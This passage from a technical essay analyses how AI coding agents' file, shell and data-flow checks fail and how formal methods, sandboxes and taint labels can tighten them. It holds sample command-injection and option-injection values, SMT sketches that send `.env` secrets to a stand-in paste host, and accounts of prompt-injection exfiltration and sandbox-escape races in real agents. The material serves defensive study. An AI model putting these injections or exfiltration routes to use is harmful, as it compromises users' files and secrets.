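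To keep paths short, Flanders replaced directory names with single letters and argued that the result carries over to longer names. That is reasonable for `..`, whose effect doesn't depend on the names around it. It fails for prefix mistakes if names in the input are also limited to single letters. With the root `/a/b`, such an encoding can't represent a case like `/work/app-old`, because no one-letter name begins with a different one. The input has to allow at least one name longer than the root's last segment, as in `/a/bc`.

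## Links, changing files and shell commands: what a path proof leaves out

A validator can be correct about every string and still let an agent write outside the permitted directory. A path is a set of directions. The operating system looks up the first name, moves to whatever it finds there, looks up the next name, and so on, and what it finds depends on the contents of the disk at that moment. Write file(p, t) for the file that the system reaches by following the path p at time t. The team wants this:

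accepted(p) ⇒ file(p, t) is under `/work/app`, where t is the moment of the write

The string proof shows only that the text of p stays under `/work/app`. Its formulas contain neither the file nor the time.

### Links

A symbolic link is a directory entry that contains another path, which the system follows when it reaches the link. If `/work/app/notes.txt` is a symbolic link to `/home/ana/notes.txt`, the first path passes every validator described so far, but an edit changes the file in Ana's home directory.

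Links also change what `..` means. If `src` is a link to `/data/src`, Linux follows `src/../main.py` to `/data/main.py`, while the depth counter places it at `/work/app/main.py`. The induction proof still holds for its list of names, but that list no longer matches the directory Linux has reached.

A path proof shows that a file is inside the allowed directory only if no link along the path leads outside it. Instead of assuming that none does, a tool can use the operating system to follow every link and then check the resulting path, called the canonical path.

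Canonical paths don't reveal hard links. A hard link is a second directory entry for the same file, and neither entry is the original. `/work/app/notes.txt` can therefore be its own canonical path while the same file also appears in Ana's home directory. A tool can check the file's link count and refuse to write if the file has more than one name, although this also blocks writes to files that some package managers hard-link on purpose. Alternatively, the tool can write a new file and rename it over the old entry, which leaves the other name pointing to the old contents. This keeps the write from changing Ana's file but doesn't stop the tool from reading it.

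In July 2026 the security company Wiz reported in *GhostApproval* that six coding assistants followed symbolic links out of the project. Wiz classified the flaw as both CWE-61 (following symbolic links) and CWE-451 (a user interface that misrepresents critical information). The second class applies because several assistants asked for approval but named the link instead of the file it pointed to.

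| Product | What the user saw | Vendor's response by 8 July 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Amazon Q Developer | An "Undo" button after the write | AWS released a fix |
| Cursor | A prompt naming the link | Cursor released a fix |
| Google Antigravity | A prompt naming the link | Google released a fix |
| Claude Code | A prompt naming the link | Anthropic rejected the report; current versions warn |
| Windsurf | Accept and reject buttons after the write | Acknowledged the report, no fix yet |
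| Augment | Nothing | Acknowledged the report, no fix yet |

AWS's *CVE-2026-12957 and CVE-2026-12958* (2026) describes the fault in Amazon Q as missing symlink validation and offers no workaround other than updating. The Hacker News' *GhostApproval Symlink Flaws Could Let Malicious Repos Run Code* (2026) found no sign that anyone had used the flaw in a real attack.

Anthropic said the scenario was outside its threat model because the user had trusted the directory and then approved the edit. It later told Wiz that its link warning had shipped in version 2.1.32, nine days before Wiz's report. Wiz lists the later version 2.1.42 for its finding and doesn't explain the discrepancy. Anthropic's argument is weak when the prompt names the wrong file. In a formula, "the user approved a write to `notes.txt`" records only that the user approved a name, but a rule that requires approval has to cover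 the file that the write will change. Wiz recommends resolving links before showing the prompt, warning when the target is outside the project, and never writing before the user has answered.

### A directory that changes after the check

Even a canonical path describes the disk only at the time of the check, and the tool writes later. Programmers call this gap a time-of-check to time-of-use (TOCTOU) race. The missing assumption is:

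file(p, t_check) = file(p, t_write)

A path proof can fail if the program checks one path and uses another. Anthropic's Python library includes a memory tool that keeps an agent's notes in a directory. According to MITRE's *Claude SDK for Python* (2026), the asynchronous version confirmed that the resolved path was inside the directory, then passed the unresolved path to the code that opened the file. Someone able to write to that directory could change a link between the check and the opening of the file. Anthropic fixed this in version 0.87.0.

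Passing on the resolved path helps but isn't enough, as Neil (2025) explains in *Traversal-resistant file APIs*. The resolved path is still text, so the system follows it again when it opens the file, and by then one of its directories may have been replaced with a link.

*Breaking the Workspace Boundary* (Jha) reports such a race in Claude Code 2.1.217 on macOS. Claude Code ran shell commands in an operating-system sandbox, which restricts the files a process can change, but ran its Edit tool outside the sandbox. Edit resolved the path when it checked permission and checked the result again later, but then opened the file by name. A program confined to the project could replace a parent directory after the second check, and Edit would write to a file outside the project.

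Jha's controls make the finding convincing. Edit blocked a direct request to change the outside file, and the sandbox blocked the confined program's attempt. An edit through the same path changed only a project file when there was no replacement, but with the replacement it changed the outside file in three consecutive runs, and the logs showed no refusal. Running code this way also required another program to load the changed file. Anthropic received the report on 22 July 2026 and two days later rated it High, at 7.7 out of 10. It paid a bounty in August but had not publicly confirmed a fix when Jha's article was published.

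A third comparison would only have narrowed the gap. Jha recommends directory handles, which refer to a directory itself instead of its name. The tool opens the permitted directory once and keeps the handle. It then opens each subdirectory relative to the previous handle, refusing links, and creates the file relative to the last handle. If another program changes what a name refers to after the tool has opened it, the write is unaffected, because the tool doesn't look that name up again.

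Linux can do the whole lookup in one call, described in the manual page *openat2(2)*. With the option `RESOLVE_BENEATH`, the kernel refuses any lookup that leaves the directory the handle refers to. The older option `O_NOFOLLOW` checks only the last segment of a path, so it doesn't protect against a replaced parent directory. If the kernel can't rule out that a `..` escaped during a race, it returns the error `EAGAIN`. The tool may try again, but it must not fall back on an ordinary open, just as a monitor must not allow a call when the solver returns `unknown`.

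The programming language Go has offered handle-based access through the `os.Root` type since version 1.24. Neil notes that it doesn't stop a path from crossing a mount point, where an administrator has attached another directory or disk. It is also open to races when Go runs on Node.js, whose file functions cannot open a path relative to a handle. An agent built on those functions needs a native component to open paths this way. Hand
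le-based access doesn't detect hard links either, because a hard link is an ordinary directory entry.

The same gap exists between whole tool calls, for instance when an agent reads a file and edits it two steps later. In *Mind the Gap*, Lilienthal and Hong (2025) reviewed 66 tasks from an existing agent benchmark by hand and judged that in 56 of them, a later call relied on something that an earlier call had read and that could have changed since. They combined risky pairs of calls into one tool, which cut the average gap in a chat environment from 1.70 to 0.07 seconds. The shorter gap makes an accidental change less likely, but an attacker who can time the change may need only a few hundredths of a second.

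### Adding the file system to the formula

A solver can reason about links and time if the formula includes them. An array can map each path to its canonical path, with one copy of the array for each moment that matters:

```
(declare-const where0 (Array String String)) ; at the check
(declare-const where1 (Array String String)) ; at the write
(declare-const p String)

(assert (str.prefixof "/work/app/" (select where0 p)))        ; passes
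(assert (not (str.prefixof "/work/app/" (select where1 p))))  ; outside
(check-sat)                                  ; sat

(assert (= (select where0 p) (select where1 p)))
(check-sat)                                  ; unsat
```

The prefix test is sound here because a canonical path contains no links and no `..`. The first answer is `sat` because nothing relates the two arrays, so the solver can choose a disk on which `p` leads somewhere else by the time of the write. The last assertion states the missing assumption from the previous section, and it concerns only one path. The rest of the disk may change, so a tool can meet the assumption by holding a handle, without freezing the file system.

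The model also shows why comparing twice didn't protect Claude Code. If the second check uses `where1` and the write uses a new array, `where2`, both checks can pass and the query is still `sat`, because `where2` can differ from `where1`.

A more detailed model would record the target of each link and compute the canonical path from these targets. Linux follows at most 40 links in one lookup, so the formula needs only a limited number of link-following steps. Creating a link becomes a `store`, and the solver can search for any sequence of, say, eight actions by the tool and another program that ends with a write outside the allowed directory. An `unsat` answer would cover every ordering of those actions, but only for the kinds of change the model includes.

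This is a good way to review a file tool's design before release, but a poor way to approve a particular call, because the monitor would first have to copy the links from the disk, and the copy could be out of date before the solver finished. The solver's running time would also lengthen the gap between checking a path and using it, which is the gap that the model describes.

### Tools that open files on their own

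The validator protects nothing if a tool doesn't call it. Relying on the proof means assuming that every file operation goes through the function it covers, and that assumption is hard to keep true in a product with many features.

Anthropic's memory tool had two implementations, and according to MITRE's record, the synchronous one was never affected. Claude Code could also write to disk through its handling of Git worktrees, which are extra working copies of a project. Rapid7, a security company, lists a flaw in which links let this feature overwrite files in the user's home directory, outside the sandbox. Anthropic fixed it in version 2.1.163. In the macOS case, Jha found that the Write tool's code performed operations in the same order as Edit's, but did not reproduce an attack through Write.

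The remedy is one function that checks and opens the file in a single operation, with no other way for a tool to reach the disk. In Go, a developer can pass each tool an `os.Root` instead of a path, and an automated code check can reject direct calls to the ordinary open functions. Tests should then cover each tool separately. For each one, Jha suggests forcing a directory replacement after the permission check and confirming that the outside file does not change.

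### Shell commands

An editing tool takes the file path as an argument, but a shell tool takes a command, which may not name the files it will change. For example, `make test` runs whatever the project's build file specifies. `cp report.txt "$OUT"` writes to a location that depends on a variable, and the same command can have a different effect after a `cd`.

Reading the paths out of the text assumes that

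files changed by the command ⊆ files named in its text

A monitor that relies on this also has to parse the text exactly as the shell does. Shodan's *Vulnerability Details CVE-2026-24053* reports that before version 2.0.74, Claude Code misread one form of output redirection in the shell zsh, so commands could write files outside the working directory without a prompt.

Even a correctly parsed command can depend on files that the monitor hasn't read. The Hacker News' *Malicious .git Configs Can Make Claude, Codex, Cursor, and Other AI Agents* (2026) reports eight flaws that could let the Git configuration in a project received from someone else run commands through seven coding agents. Four had no fix when the article appeared in September.

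Lists of forbidden commands can also be bypassed. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) describes ShellSieve, a system that uses a language model to propose ways around such lists and tries them in a sandbox. In tests of 1,709 lists from GitHub, between 69.0 and 98.6 percent were fragile, depending on the kind of bypass. Soteria's rule against four spellings of a deletion command has the same weakness.

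An honest contract for a shell tool is that it may change any file the process has permission to change. The solver then has nothing with which to rule out a violation:

```
(declare-sort File 0)
(declare-fun inside (File) Bool)
(declare-fun writes (String File) Bool)      ; command, file
(declare-const f File)

(assert (writes "make test" f))
(assert (not (inside f)))
(check-sat)                                  ; sat

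(assert (=> (writes "make test" f) (inside f)))
(check-sat)                                  ; unsat
```

The last assertion states what an operating-system sandbox is supposed to guarantee. It directly contradicts the violation, so the solver adds almost nothing to this proof, and whether the rule holds depends on the sandbox.

### Why a check needs a sandbox, and a sandbox a check

In a sandbox, the kernel restricts a process and every program it starts. The kernel allows or blocks a file change when a program attempts it, so it doesn't need to predict the effect from the command's text. In Jha's tests, Seatbelt, the sandbox built into macOS, worked as configured.

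The weakness was that Edit ran outside the sandbox. GitLab's *CVE-2026-39861* (2026) describes an earlier flaw that also involved both a sandboxed command and an unsandboxed part of Claude Code. The command could create a link to a location outside the project, and the unsandboxed part would follow it when writing. Neither could write outside the project alone. Anthropic fixed that flaw in version 2.1.64, and Jha found the race in a later version. Putting the file tools in a sandbox as well would limit the damage from both defects, because the kernel would refuse the final write even if the tool's path check had passed.

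Sandboxes also have flaws. CodeAnt AI, which published Jha's report, found another flaw in Claude Code's macOS sandbox that occurred only when the project's path contained wildcard characters. This suggests that sandbox rules can contain the same translation errors as the globs in a permission policy. Rashidi also describes a benchmark in which capable language models found and exploited weaknesses that researchers had planted in containers, a common form of sandbox.

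A working sandbox is also too coarse for many rules. If the agent may write in `/work/app`, the sandbox will let it delete everything there. The sandbox also doesn't record whether a person approved an edit or whether the agent read the file first. A check on the tool call can enforce such rules and explain a refusal so that the agent tries something else. YoloFS, another system in Rashidi's survey, addresses damage within the permitted directory by staging changes and keeping snapshots, so that a person can review or undo them.

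How much each layer contributes is unclear. Rashidi found that researchers almost never test isolation and access control against each other on a shared benchmark. The argument for combining them is that they cover different failures. A sandbox can contain a shell command whose effects nobody predicted, and a check can refuse an edit that the sandbox would allow. Neither a path check nor a limit on writes stops a command from reading a password inside the project and sending it over the network. Preventing that requires rules about where the data goes.

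## Tracking secret data into outputs and commands

Suppose an agent reads the `.env` file with a project's passwords, formats the contents and posts the result to a web address. Each call can pass its own check, because the file is inside the project, formatting text is harmless, and the agent is allowed to post to the web. Together, the calls leak the passwords, because the posted text derives from the file. To catch this, a checker puts a taint label on the secret where it enters the plan and works out which later values also receive the label.

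### Sources, sinks and the rules between them

The developer first marks the sources of secret data. `read_file` is a source when the path is `.env`, but not when it is `README.md`. One secret can have several sources. Many programs load `.env` into environment variables when they start, so a tool that prints those variables must also be marked as a source.

Sinks have to be marked argument by argument. When an agent posts to the web, a secret can leave in the body or in the URL, for instance after the question mark. Whether an argument counts as a sink may depend on another argument. In Meijer's mailbox example, whether the body of an email is a sink depends on the recipient.

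Some sinks are easy to overlook. *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* (Balunović, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2024) describes an agent that summarises customer feedback from a spreadsheet and sends the summary to its user on Slack, a chat service. An attacker uses a planted comment to make the agent include a link to the attacker's site, with the spreadsheet's contents encoded in the address. Slack opens links to show a preview, so the attacker's server receives the contents even though the message went only to the user. The attack worked on two widely used agent systems, whose makers have since fixed the vulnerability. A rule that checks only the recipient would miss this attack, so Balunović and colleagues treat a Slack message as a sink whenever link previews are on.

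Next, each tool needs a propagation rule, which gives the label on its result:

| Step | Label afterwards |
|---|---|
| `format(text)` | The result has the label of `text` |
| `join(a, b)` | The result has a label if `a` or `b` has one |
| `copy(src, dst)` | The file `dst` has the label of `src` |
| `current_time()` | None |
| `redact(text)` | None, because the developer permits this declassification |

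If nobody knows what a tool does with its input, the cautious rule is to pass every label on. This can cause false alarms but doesn't hide a leak. More precise rules take work, and Kishor, Nicolet and Dodds (2026), in *Soundness Checking of Taint Flow Models*, had a language model write them for library methods in the programming language Go. These sets of rules are called taint flow models, and a separate program checked them. A rule is sound only if every flow it leaves out is impossible, which the program tried to prove from the method's types and use of memory. In a test on 97 taint flow models from six large codebases, the program proved them sound for 93 percent of the methods they covered. A developer can apply the cautious rule to the rest.

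The last list contains the permitted declassifications. In *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026), a tool called `Sanitize` selects the approved fields of a confidential report, and the policy marks its result as public while the original report stays confidential. Changing a label does not remove any data. The solver assumes that the tool drops the secret fields, and the declaration is correct only if it does. A person can also approve a release. In *Agenra*, each approval covers one exact call and can be used only once, so the agent needs a new approval if it edits the text afterwards.

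### Labels with more than two levels

A label that is either present or absent is the simplest case of the scheme in Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976). The scheme has a set of security classes and a relation between them, written A → B, which means that information in class A may flow into class B. An operation, ⊕, combines the classes of two values to give the class of a value computed from them.

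A two-level policy has the classes L (not confidential) and H (confidential), and it allows every flow except H → L. L ⊕ L is L, and any combination that includes H is H, so if an agent inserts one password into a page of public text, the whole page becomes confidential.

Denning's four-level example uses the government classes unclassified, confidential, secret and top secret. Information may stay at its level or move up, and ⊕ gives the higher of two levels. A summary of one confidential and one secret document is therefore secret. It may go into a secret or top secret archive, but not into a confidential one.

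In both examples, ⊕ returns the lowest class into which both inputs may flow, because a lower class would permit a leak and a higher one would block harmless uses. Classes form a lattice when they have this operation and a matching one that returns the highest class that may flow into both inputs. Permitted flows can be chained (if A → B and B → C, then A → C), so a sequence of steps is secure when each step is secure, and a checker can go through a plan one step at a time.

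Classes can also be sets of properties instead of ranked levels. Denning describes a system with medical, financial and criminal records, where a destination must have every property of the data it receives. An agent's operator could use "credentials" and "customer data" as properties in the same way, so that a payment company may receive customer data but never credentials. In a formula, levels are integers combined by taking the larger one, and properties are separate Boolean variables combined with "or".

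### The .env plan as a formula

Here is the plan from the start of the section:

```
text   = read_file(".env")
report = format(text)
post(host, report)
```

The name of the server, `host`, comes from a settings file that nobody has read yet. The policy allows secrets to go only to `ci.example.com`, the team's own build server. Each value gets a Boolean variable for its label:

```
(declare-const secret-text Bool)       ; label on the file's contents
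(declare-const secret-report Bool)     ; label on the formatted text
(declare-const host String)            ; where the report goes

(assert secret-text)                   ; .env is a source
(assert (= secret-report secret-text)) ; format passes the label on

; a labelled value reaches a server off the allowlist
(assert (and secret-report (distinct host "ci.example.com")))
(check-sat)                            ; sat: e.g. host = "paste.example.net"

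(assert (= host "ci.example.com"))     ; the plan checks host first
(check-sat)                            ; unsat
```

The first answer describes a leak, since the settings file may name any server. If the plan posts only after checking `host` against the allowlist, no leak remains in the model.

This encoding errs on the side of safety when a rule is missing. Without the equation for `format`, nothing determines `secret-report`, so the solver may set it to true and cause a false alarm. The same happens if the rules don't state whether a file is a source. An ordinary program that stores labels in a table and assumes "no label" for missing entries would instead let the secret through.

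The variable holds the server's name, which ordinary code has to extract from the full address with a URL parser. Testing whether the address starts with `https://ci.example.com` would repeat the prefix mistake from file paths, because `https://ci.example.com.attacker.net` passes. The proof also assumes that `post` doesn't follow a redirect to a different server.

A secret can leak without anyone copying it. Suppose a plan posts the word "ready" only if `.env` contains a key for live payments. The message body is a constant without a label, but the recipient can learn from it that the file contains such a key. Denning calls this an implicit flow, and it exists even when the message isn't sent, because its absence also reveals something about the file. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes a system that labels a complete plan before it runs. To cover implicit flows, the system adds a condition's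 label to every step in both branches, so the call that posts "ready" counts as secret.

### When a solver adds something to graph search

A simpler method also finds the leak in the `.env` plan. It represents each value as a node, with an arrow from each input to each result, and follows the arrows from the source to see whether they reach a sink. The static analysers CodeQL and Semgrep, which Meijer suggests, work this way. If every route in the graph can occur, a solver adds nothing to this reachability search. The same is true with lattice labels. Girrens and Wang compute them in one pass through the plan, and *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* described a check in 1977 simple enough to build into most compilers of the time.

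A solver helps when conditions rule out some of the routes. In this plan, redaction and sending both happen exactly when `mode` is "prod":

```
report = format(read_file(".env"))
if mode = "prod":  report = redact(report)
if mode = "prod":  post("paste.example.net", report)
```

The graph contains a route that skips `redact` and then reaches `post`. To follow it, `mode` would have to differ from "prod" on the second line and equal "prod" on the third. A search that ignores conditions reports a leak anyway. The solver takes the conditions into account:

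```
(declare-const mode String)            ; fixed before the plan runs
(define-fun redacted () Bool (= mode "prod"))
(define-fun sent () Bool (= mode "prod"))

(push)
(assert (and sent (not redacted)))
(check-sat)                            ; unsat
(pop)

; a later version sends in every mode except "dev"
(define-fun sent2 () Bool (distinct mode "dev"))
(assert (and sent2 (not redacted)))
(check-sat)                            ; sat: e.g. mode = "staging"
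```

In the later version, the plan sends unredacted secrets whenever `mode` is "staging". Both versions have the same graph, so graph search gives the same warning for each. A developer who has learned to dismiss the warning about the safe version will probably dismiss this one too, even though it is correct.

The `unsat` answer assumes that `mode` has the same value on both lines. If the plan reads the setting twice and someone can change it in between, the formula needs two variables, and the answer becomes `sat`. The setting also must not come from `.env`, because then whether a message arrives would reveal part of the file, which is an implicit flow.

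Often the easiest repair is to put `redact` and `post` under the same condition, which removes the route without redaction from the graph and makes the solver unnecessary. *Can Formal Methods Apply to Agent Security?*, a blog post by joe-b-security, argues that a graph suits most organisations better than a proof. The team would record its agents, tools, permissions and data flows as facts, and after every change query them for a route from an untrusted source to a powerful tool. This works for reviewing a whole system, where an unexpected connection matters more than the exact condition on a branch, but it would not distinguish the two versions of this plan.

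Soteria's verifier keeps track of branch conditions, so when different branches pass different variables to a tool, it checks each variable only under the condition of its branch. The example rule in He and colleagues requires a data flow instead of forbidding one. The amount of a refund must derive from an earlier lookup of the reservation, so that the agent can't invent it. The cautious rule for unknown tools, which passes labels from input to output, is unsafe here. If a tool ignores its input, an invented amount appears to come from the reservation. The requirement is also weak, since a refund of ten times the fare would still derive from the reservation.

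Soteria would need extra rules to catch the `.env` leak. It tags each value a tool returns with that tool alone. If formatting is a tool call, `report` gets the `format` tag but not the `read_file` tag. The rule's author would have to spell out the chain from one tool to the next.

### Untrusted data

Rules about secrets protect confidentiality by limiting where data may go. They don't protect integrity, which is about what data may influence an action. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay an invoice in which an attacker has replaced the account number. The money goes to the attacker even though the invoice contains no planted instruction, the agent makes the right calls in the right order, and no secret leaks. To prevent this, the policy has to require a trusted value for the account argument.

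Girrens and Wang give each value *x* two labels, C(*x*) for confidentiality and I(*x*) for integrity. Data may flow from *s* to *d* if

C(*s*) ≤ C(*d*) and I(*d*) ≤ I(*s*)

The destination must be cleared for data at least as secret as the source, and the source must be at least as trusted as the destination requires. When a tool combines two values, the result is as secret as the more secret one and only as trusted as the less trusted one.

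The integrity half is expensive. Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4-nano on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in simulated office, chat, travel and banking systems:

| | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks, of 949 |
|---|---|---|
| Plan fixed in advance, no label checks | 53.0% | 4 |
| With label checks | 29.0% | 0 |

With the checks on, SPA rejected about 53 percent of the runs before any tool ran, usually because a plan passed a tool's untrusted output to an action that required trusted input. Many ordinary requests, such as paying the amount stated in a bill, require passing data this way.

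In this test, the labels stopped four attacks but reduced the number of completed tasks by almost half. The result probably understates the labels' value, because the attacks mostly planted instructions, which a plan fixed in advance already resists. Attacks that swap an account number would be a better test of integrity labels. Some of the drop in completed tasks comes from SPA's design. Its planner gets only one attempt, whereas Soteria's can revise a rejected plan. SPA also has no way to raise a value's integrity after a check, which would be the counterpart of declassification. And it sets one minimum level of trust for all of a tool's inputs, so a single untrusted argument blocks the call.

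Shivakumar and colleagues instead write rules for individual arguments. Their example agent may send a report to Alice only once. Her address must come from the company directory, and the body must come from `Sanitize`, even if another tool returns identical text. Shivakumar and colleagues point out that this policy still lets the agent run `Sanitize` on an attacker's document and send the result. A second rule requires the input of `Sanitize` to come from the tool that reads the report. This rule rejects the attacker's plan and still allows all six legitimate orders of the calls.

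### Secrets in command lines

A shell command can reveal a secret through any of its arguments, such as the URL given to the download program `curl`. Even a command that makes no network connection can expose a secret, because other users on a typical Linux system can see the arguments of running programs.

The text of a command may not show that a secret is involved. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, give an example with three commands, shortened here:

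```
curl --json @report.txt https://api.github.com   # allowed
cp servers.csv report.txt                        # allowed
curl --json @report.txt https://api.github.com   # denied
```

The first and third commands are identical, but by the third, `report.txt` contains a confidential list of servers. Each file therefore needs a label that changes with its contents. In a formula, an array can map file names to labels, and a single `store` operation can represent the copy. A monitor that knows all the file names can update a table instead.

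The monitor also has to determine which files a command reads and writes. The text of `make test` doesn't list them, so a safe rule based on the text alone would have to pass the label of every readable file to everything the command writes or sends. Tether narrows this down by recording the requests that each command makes to the operating system. It runs the command in a disposable layer over the file system, holds back network traffic, and makes the changes permanent only if the policy allows them. If a program reads one file and later writes another, Tether treats the second as dependent on the first, even if the program copied nothing.

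Sistla and colleagues tested Tether by replaying recorded runs of coding agents from two benchmarks. Tether blocked every attack they counted as in scope and wrongly blocked 2.3 percent of the harmless runs on one benchmark and 5.0 percent on the other. They excluded attacks that break no rule about data flow and attacks that move data through a database or a background service. Tether can refuse to contact a database or service but can't trace data through it. Every task used the same policy except for the list of sensitive files, which somebody has to supply.

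### Untrusted text that changes a command

Suppose an agent commits its changes to Git, the version control program, and takes the commit message from the title of a bug report that a stranger wrote. The tool pastes the title between single quotes and passes the line to a shell. If the title is `x' --amend -m 'y`, the shell receives this:

```
git commit -m 'x' --amend -m 'y'
```

The quote after `x` ends the message, and the rest of the title becomes options. Git now replaces the previous commit instead of adding a new one. No secret has moved, so a check of confidentiality labels would pass. This is an integrity failure, because untrusted text has changed what the command does. Attackers do the same to databases in SQL injection, which Meijer compares to prompt injection.

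Banning untrusted text from commands altogether would be too strict, since a stranger's title is perfectly acceptable as a message. The tool needs to keep the title in its place. The most reliable way is to use structured arguments, which means starting the program directly with a list such as `["git", "commit", "-m", title]`. No shell reads the title, so Git receives it as one argument whatever characters it contains. The policy can then treat each argument separately:

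| Argument | Secret value | Untrusted value |
|---|---|---|
| Body of a web request | Only to servers on the allowlist | Yes |
| Address of a web request | No | Only if the request contains no secret |
| Commit message | No | Yes |
| Script for `sh -c` | No | No |

The last row is there because structured arguments don't help when the program treats an argument as code. They also don't stop a value from being read as an option. If a tool runs `["sort", name]` and the name is `--output=main.py`, `sort` overwrites `main.py`. Placing `--` before the name makes `sort` treat it as a file name instead.

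If a tool can't avoid the shell, the formula needs a model of quoting. In the usual Linux shells, the only character with a special meaning between single quotes is another single quote. Suppose a validator rejects titles that contain `;`, `|` or `&`, which separate or connect commands. The query asks whether an accepted title can end the quoted text:

```
(declare-const title String)
(define-fun rejected () RegLan         ; contains ; or | or &
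  (re.++ re.all
         (re.union (str.to_re ";") (str.to_re "|") (str.to_re "&"))
         re.all))
(assert (not (str.in_re title rejected)))
(assert (str.contains title "'"))      ; can end the quoted text
(check-sat)                            ; sat
```

The title with `--amend` is one such case. Rejecting single quotes as well would prevent this, but it would also block a title like "Don't crash on start". The standard fix is to replace each single quote with `'\''`, which ends the quoted text, adds a literal quote and starts quoting again.

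An induction like the one for the depth counter shows that this escaping works. The invariant is that the shell is inside quotes before each character of the title. An ordinary character doesn't change that, and the four characters that replace a quote also leave the shell inside quotes. The proof holds only if the model matches the real shell. The Windows command prompt doesn't treat single quotes as quotation marks, so the escaping doesn't work there.

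### From trace rules to labels

An early policy language for agents did without labels. Invariant Labs' *Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* (2024) presented the language that Balunović and colleagues had designed at the company. Its rules describe forbidden patterns in the trace, the list of messages, tool calls and results so far. A rule for the `.env` plan might look like this:

```
raise "possible leak" if:
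    (out: ToolOutput) -> (call: ToolCall)
    out.tool is tool:read_file
    call is tool:post
```

The arrow means only that `out` comes before `call` in the trace, not that data flows from one to the other. The analyser tries every pair of events and needs no solver, since a trace of 100 events has only 4,950 pairs. Once the agent has read any file, this rule blocks every later post, even one unrelated to the file. But if the agent copies `.env` with one shell command and uploads the copy with another, the rule doesn't match, because neither `read_file` nor `post` appears in the trace.

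One published example also shows how easy it is to get such a rule wrong. Balunović and colleagues write that after an agent reads a document containing personal information, it may send email only to the document's owner. But the rule they printed raises an error when the recipient is the owner and permits email to everyone else.

Snyk, a software security company, bought Invariant Labs in June 2025, according to SiliconANGLE's *Snyk acquires Invariant Labs expand AI agent security capabilities* (2025). By then Invariant Labs sold a rule engine for agents as Guardrails. In research, labels that move with the data have replaced the arrow. Agenra attaches them to values, Tether attaches them to files, and *SafeFlow* (2026) copies them along the messages between several agents. In SafeFlow's example, one agent reads a user's login configuration, a second rewrites the text, and a third prepares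 an email to an outsider. Each step could pass on its own, but the labels reach the email, so SafeFlow blocks it.

The second agent in that example is a language model, and SafeFlow labels its output without examining how the model used the text. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) points out that taint analysis for ordinary programs can't be applied directly to a step performed by a language model.

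## Secret data that passes through the language model

Taint analysis works on ordinary code because each instruction has a known effect. After `b = a + 1`, the value of `b` depends only on `a`. A language model produces its next output from its whole context (the text it has received so far), and nobody can reliably compute which parts of the context a given word depends on. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) lists this as an open challenge.

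Suppose an agent reads `.env` to find out why a program won't start, then writes to an outside support desk. The message might quote the database password, or it might only mention that the password contains a quotation mark. *Ghost in the Agent* counts a flow as explicit even if the output contains the data in transformed form. A filter that searches outgoing text for the password catches an exact copy but misses the password spelt backwards.

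The cautious approach is to assume that every output depends on the whole context. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) therefore gives a model's output the combined label of all the messages the model received. The output then joins the context, so the context's label can rise during a conversation but never fall. After the agent has read `.env`, all its later outputs count as secret, including those that use nothing from the file.

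When labels list permitted readers, the restrictions on the model's output quickly become a burden as it reads more documents. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, anything the model writes after reading both may go only to Ben and Carla. After a dozen documents, perhaps only the user may still read what it writes.

Some researchers try to narrow the label. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and colleagues that estimates which messages influenced an answer, then generates the answer again from those messages alone, so the new answer can have a lower label. *AgentKernel* (2026) labels each item in an agent's memory according to the pieces of text that support it. If an attacker writes text that blurs where an item came from, the item's label may be too low. A single label for the whole session avoids that risk, but *AgentKernel*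 calls it unusable because one untrusted web page taints everything.

### One label for the whole session

Microsoft researchers built a system around a session label and described it in *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (Schneider, Faujdar and colleagues, 2026). Data is public, internal, confidential or restricted, and the session takes the highest level the agent has touched:

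session level ← max(session level, level of the new data)

A separate flag records whether any of the data must stay inside the organisation, and it never resets either. In one example, an agent reads salaries and then tries to upload a file to the cloud. The system blocks the upload and ends the session, even if the file contains no salaries.

Another check runs before the session starts and uses the levels that each tool declares. Schneider and colleagues tried every combination of the 16 policies that govern their 32 tools:

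| Rule at the start of a session | Pairs of policies blocked | Triples blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Every tool must be cleared for the highest level present | 79.2% | 95.5% |
| Levels may mix, but nothing above public may leave | 42.5% | 60.5% |

These are shares of possible combinations, not of tasks that anyone wants done. Schneider and colleagues didn't measure how many tasks were completed or how many attacks were stopped, and they point out that the rates depend on how a catalog's tools are spread across the levels. Under both rules, the email policy conflicts with all 15 others, so an agent that can send email can't also read files or search the web. An agent with a shell can't fetch a web page in the same session, even if it never reads a secret. In one of the team's examples of a harmless session, an agent queries a shareable product list in a database and posts a summary to Slack. The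 check at the start would reject this session because the database tool is declared confidential.

Schneider and colleagues defend the strictness by arguing that a team can notice and correct a wrongly blocked task, but can't take back a leaked document. They suggest splitting long workflows into shorter ones. This is safe only if each new session starts with the label of the data it receives. Their system makes that label optional, and a session without one starts as public.

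### Keeping the secret away from the planner

A system can avoid most of this over-labelling if the model that chooses the actions never reads the secret. CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented in 2025, divides the work between two models. According to Girrens and Wang, a privileged model translates the user's request into code, and a quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the data. The privileged model never sees the values that the code produces. For the program that won't start, the code might be:

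```
env   = read_file(".env")
cause = quarantined_llm("Why does the program not start?", env)
send(support_desk, cause)
```

The software that runs the code records where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks this against the tool's policy before every call. Since `cause` derives from `env`, a policy on secrets blocks the last line. But a later step that posts an unrelated status update can still run, because the model that planned it never read the passwords.

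Papers differ on how much CaMeL reduces task completion. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) calls the reduction on AgentDojo comparatively modest. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that switching on CaMeL's policy checks halves the share of banking tasks it completes. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025), by two employees of a security company, gives a completion rate of 67 percent for the whole benchmark, but the reference for this figure leads to an unrelated paper.

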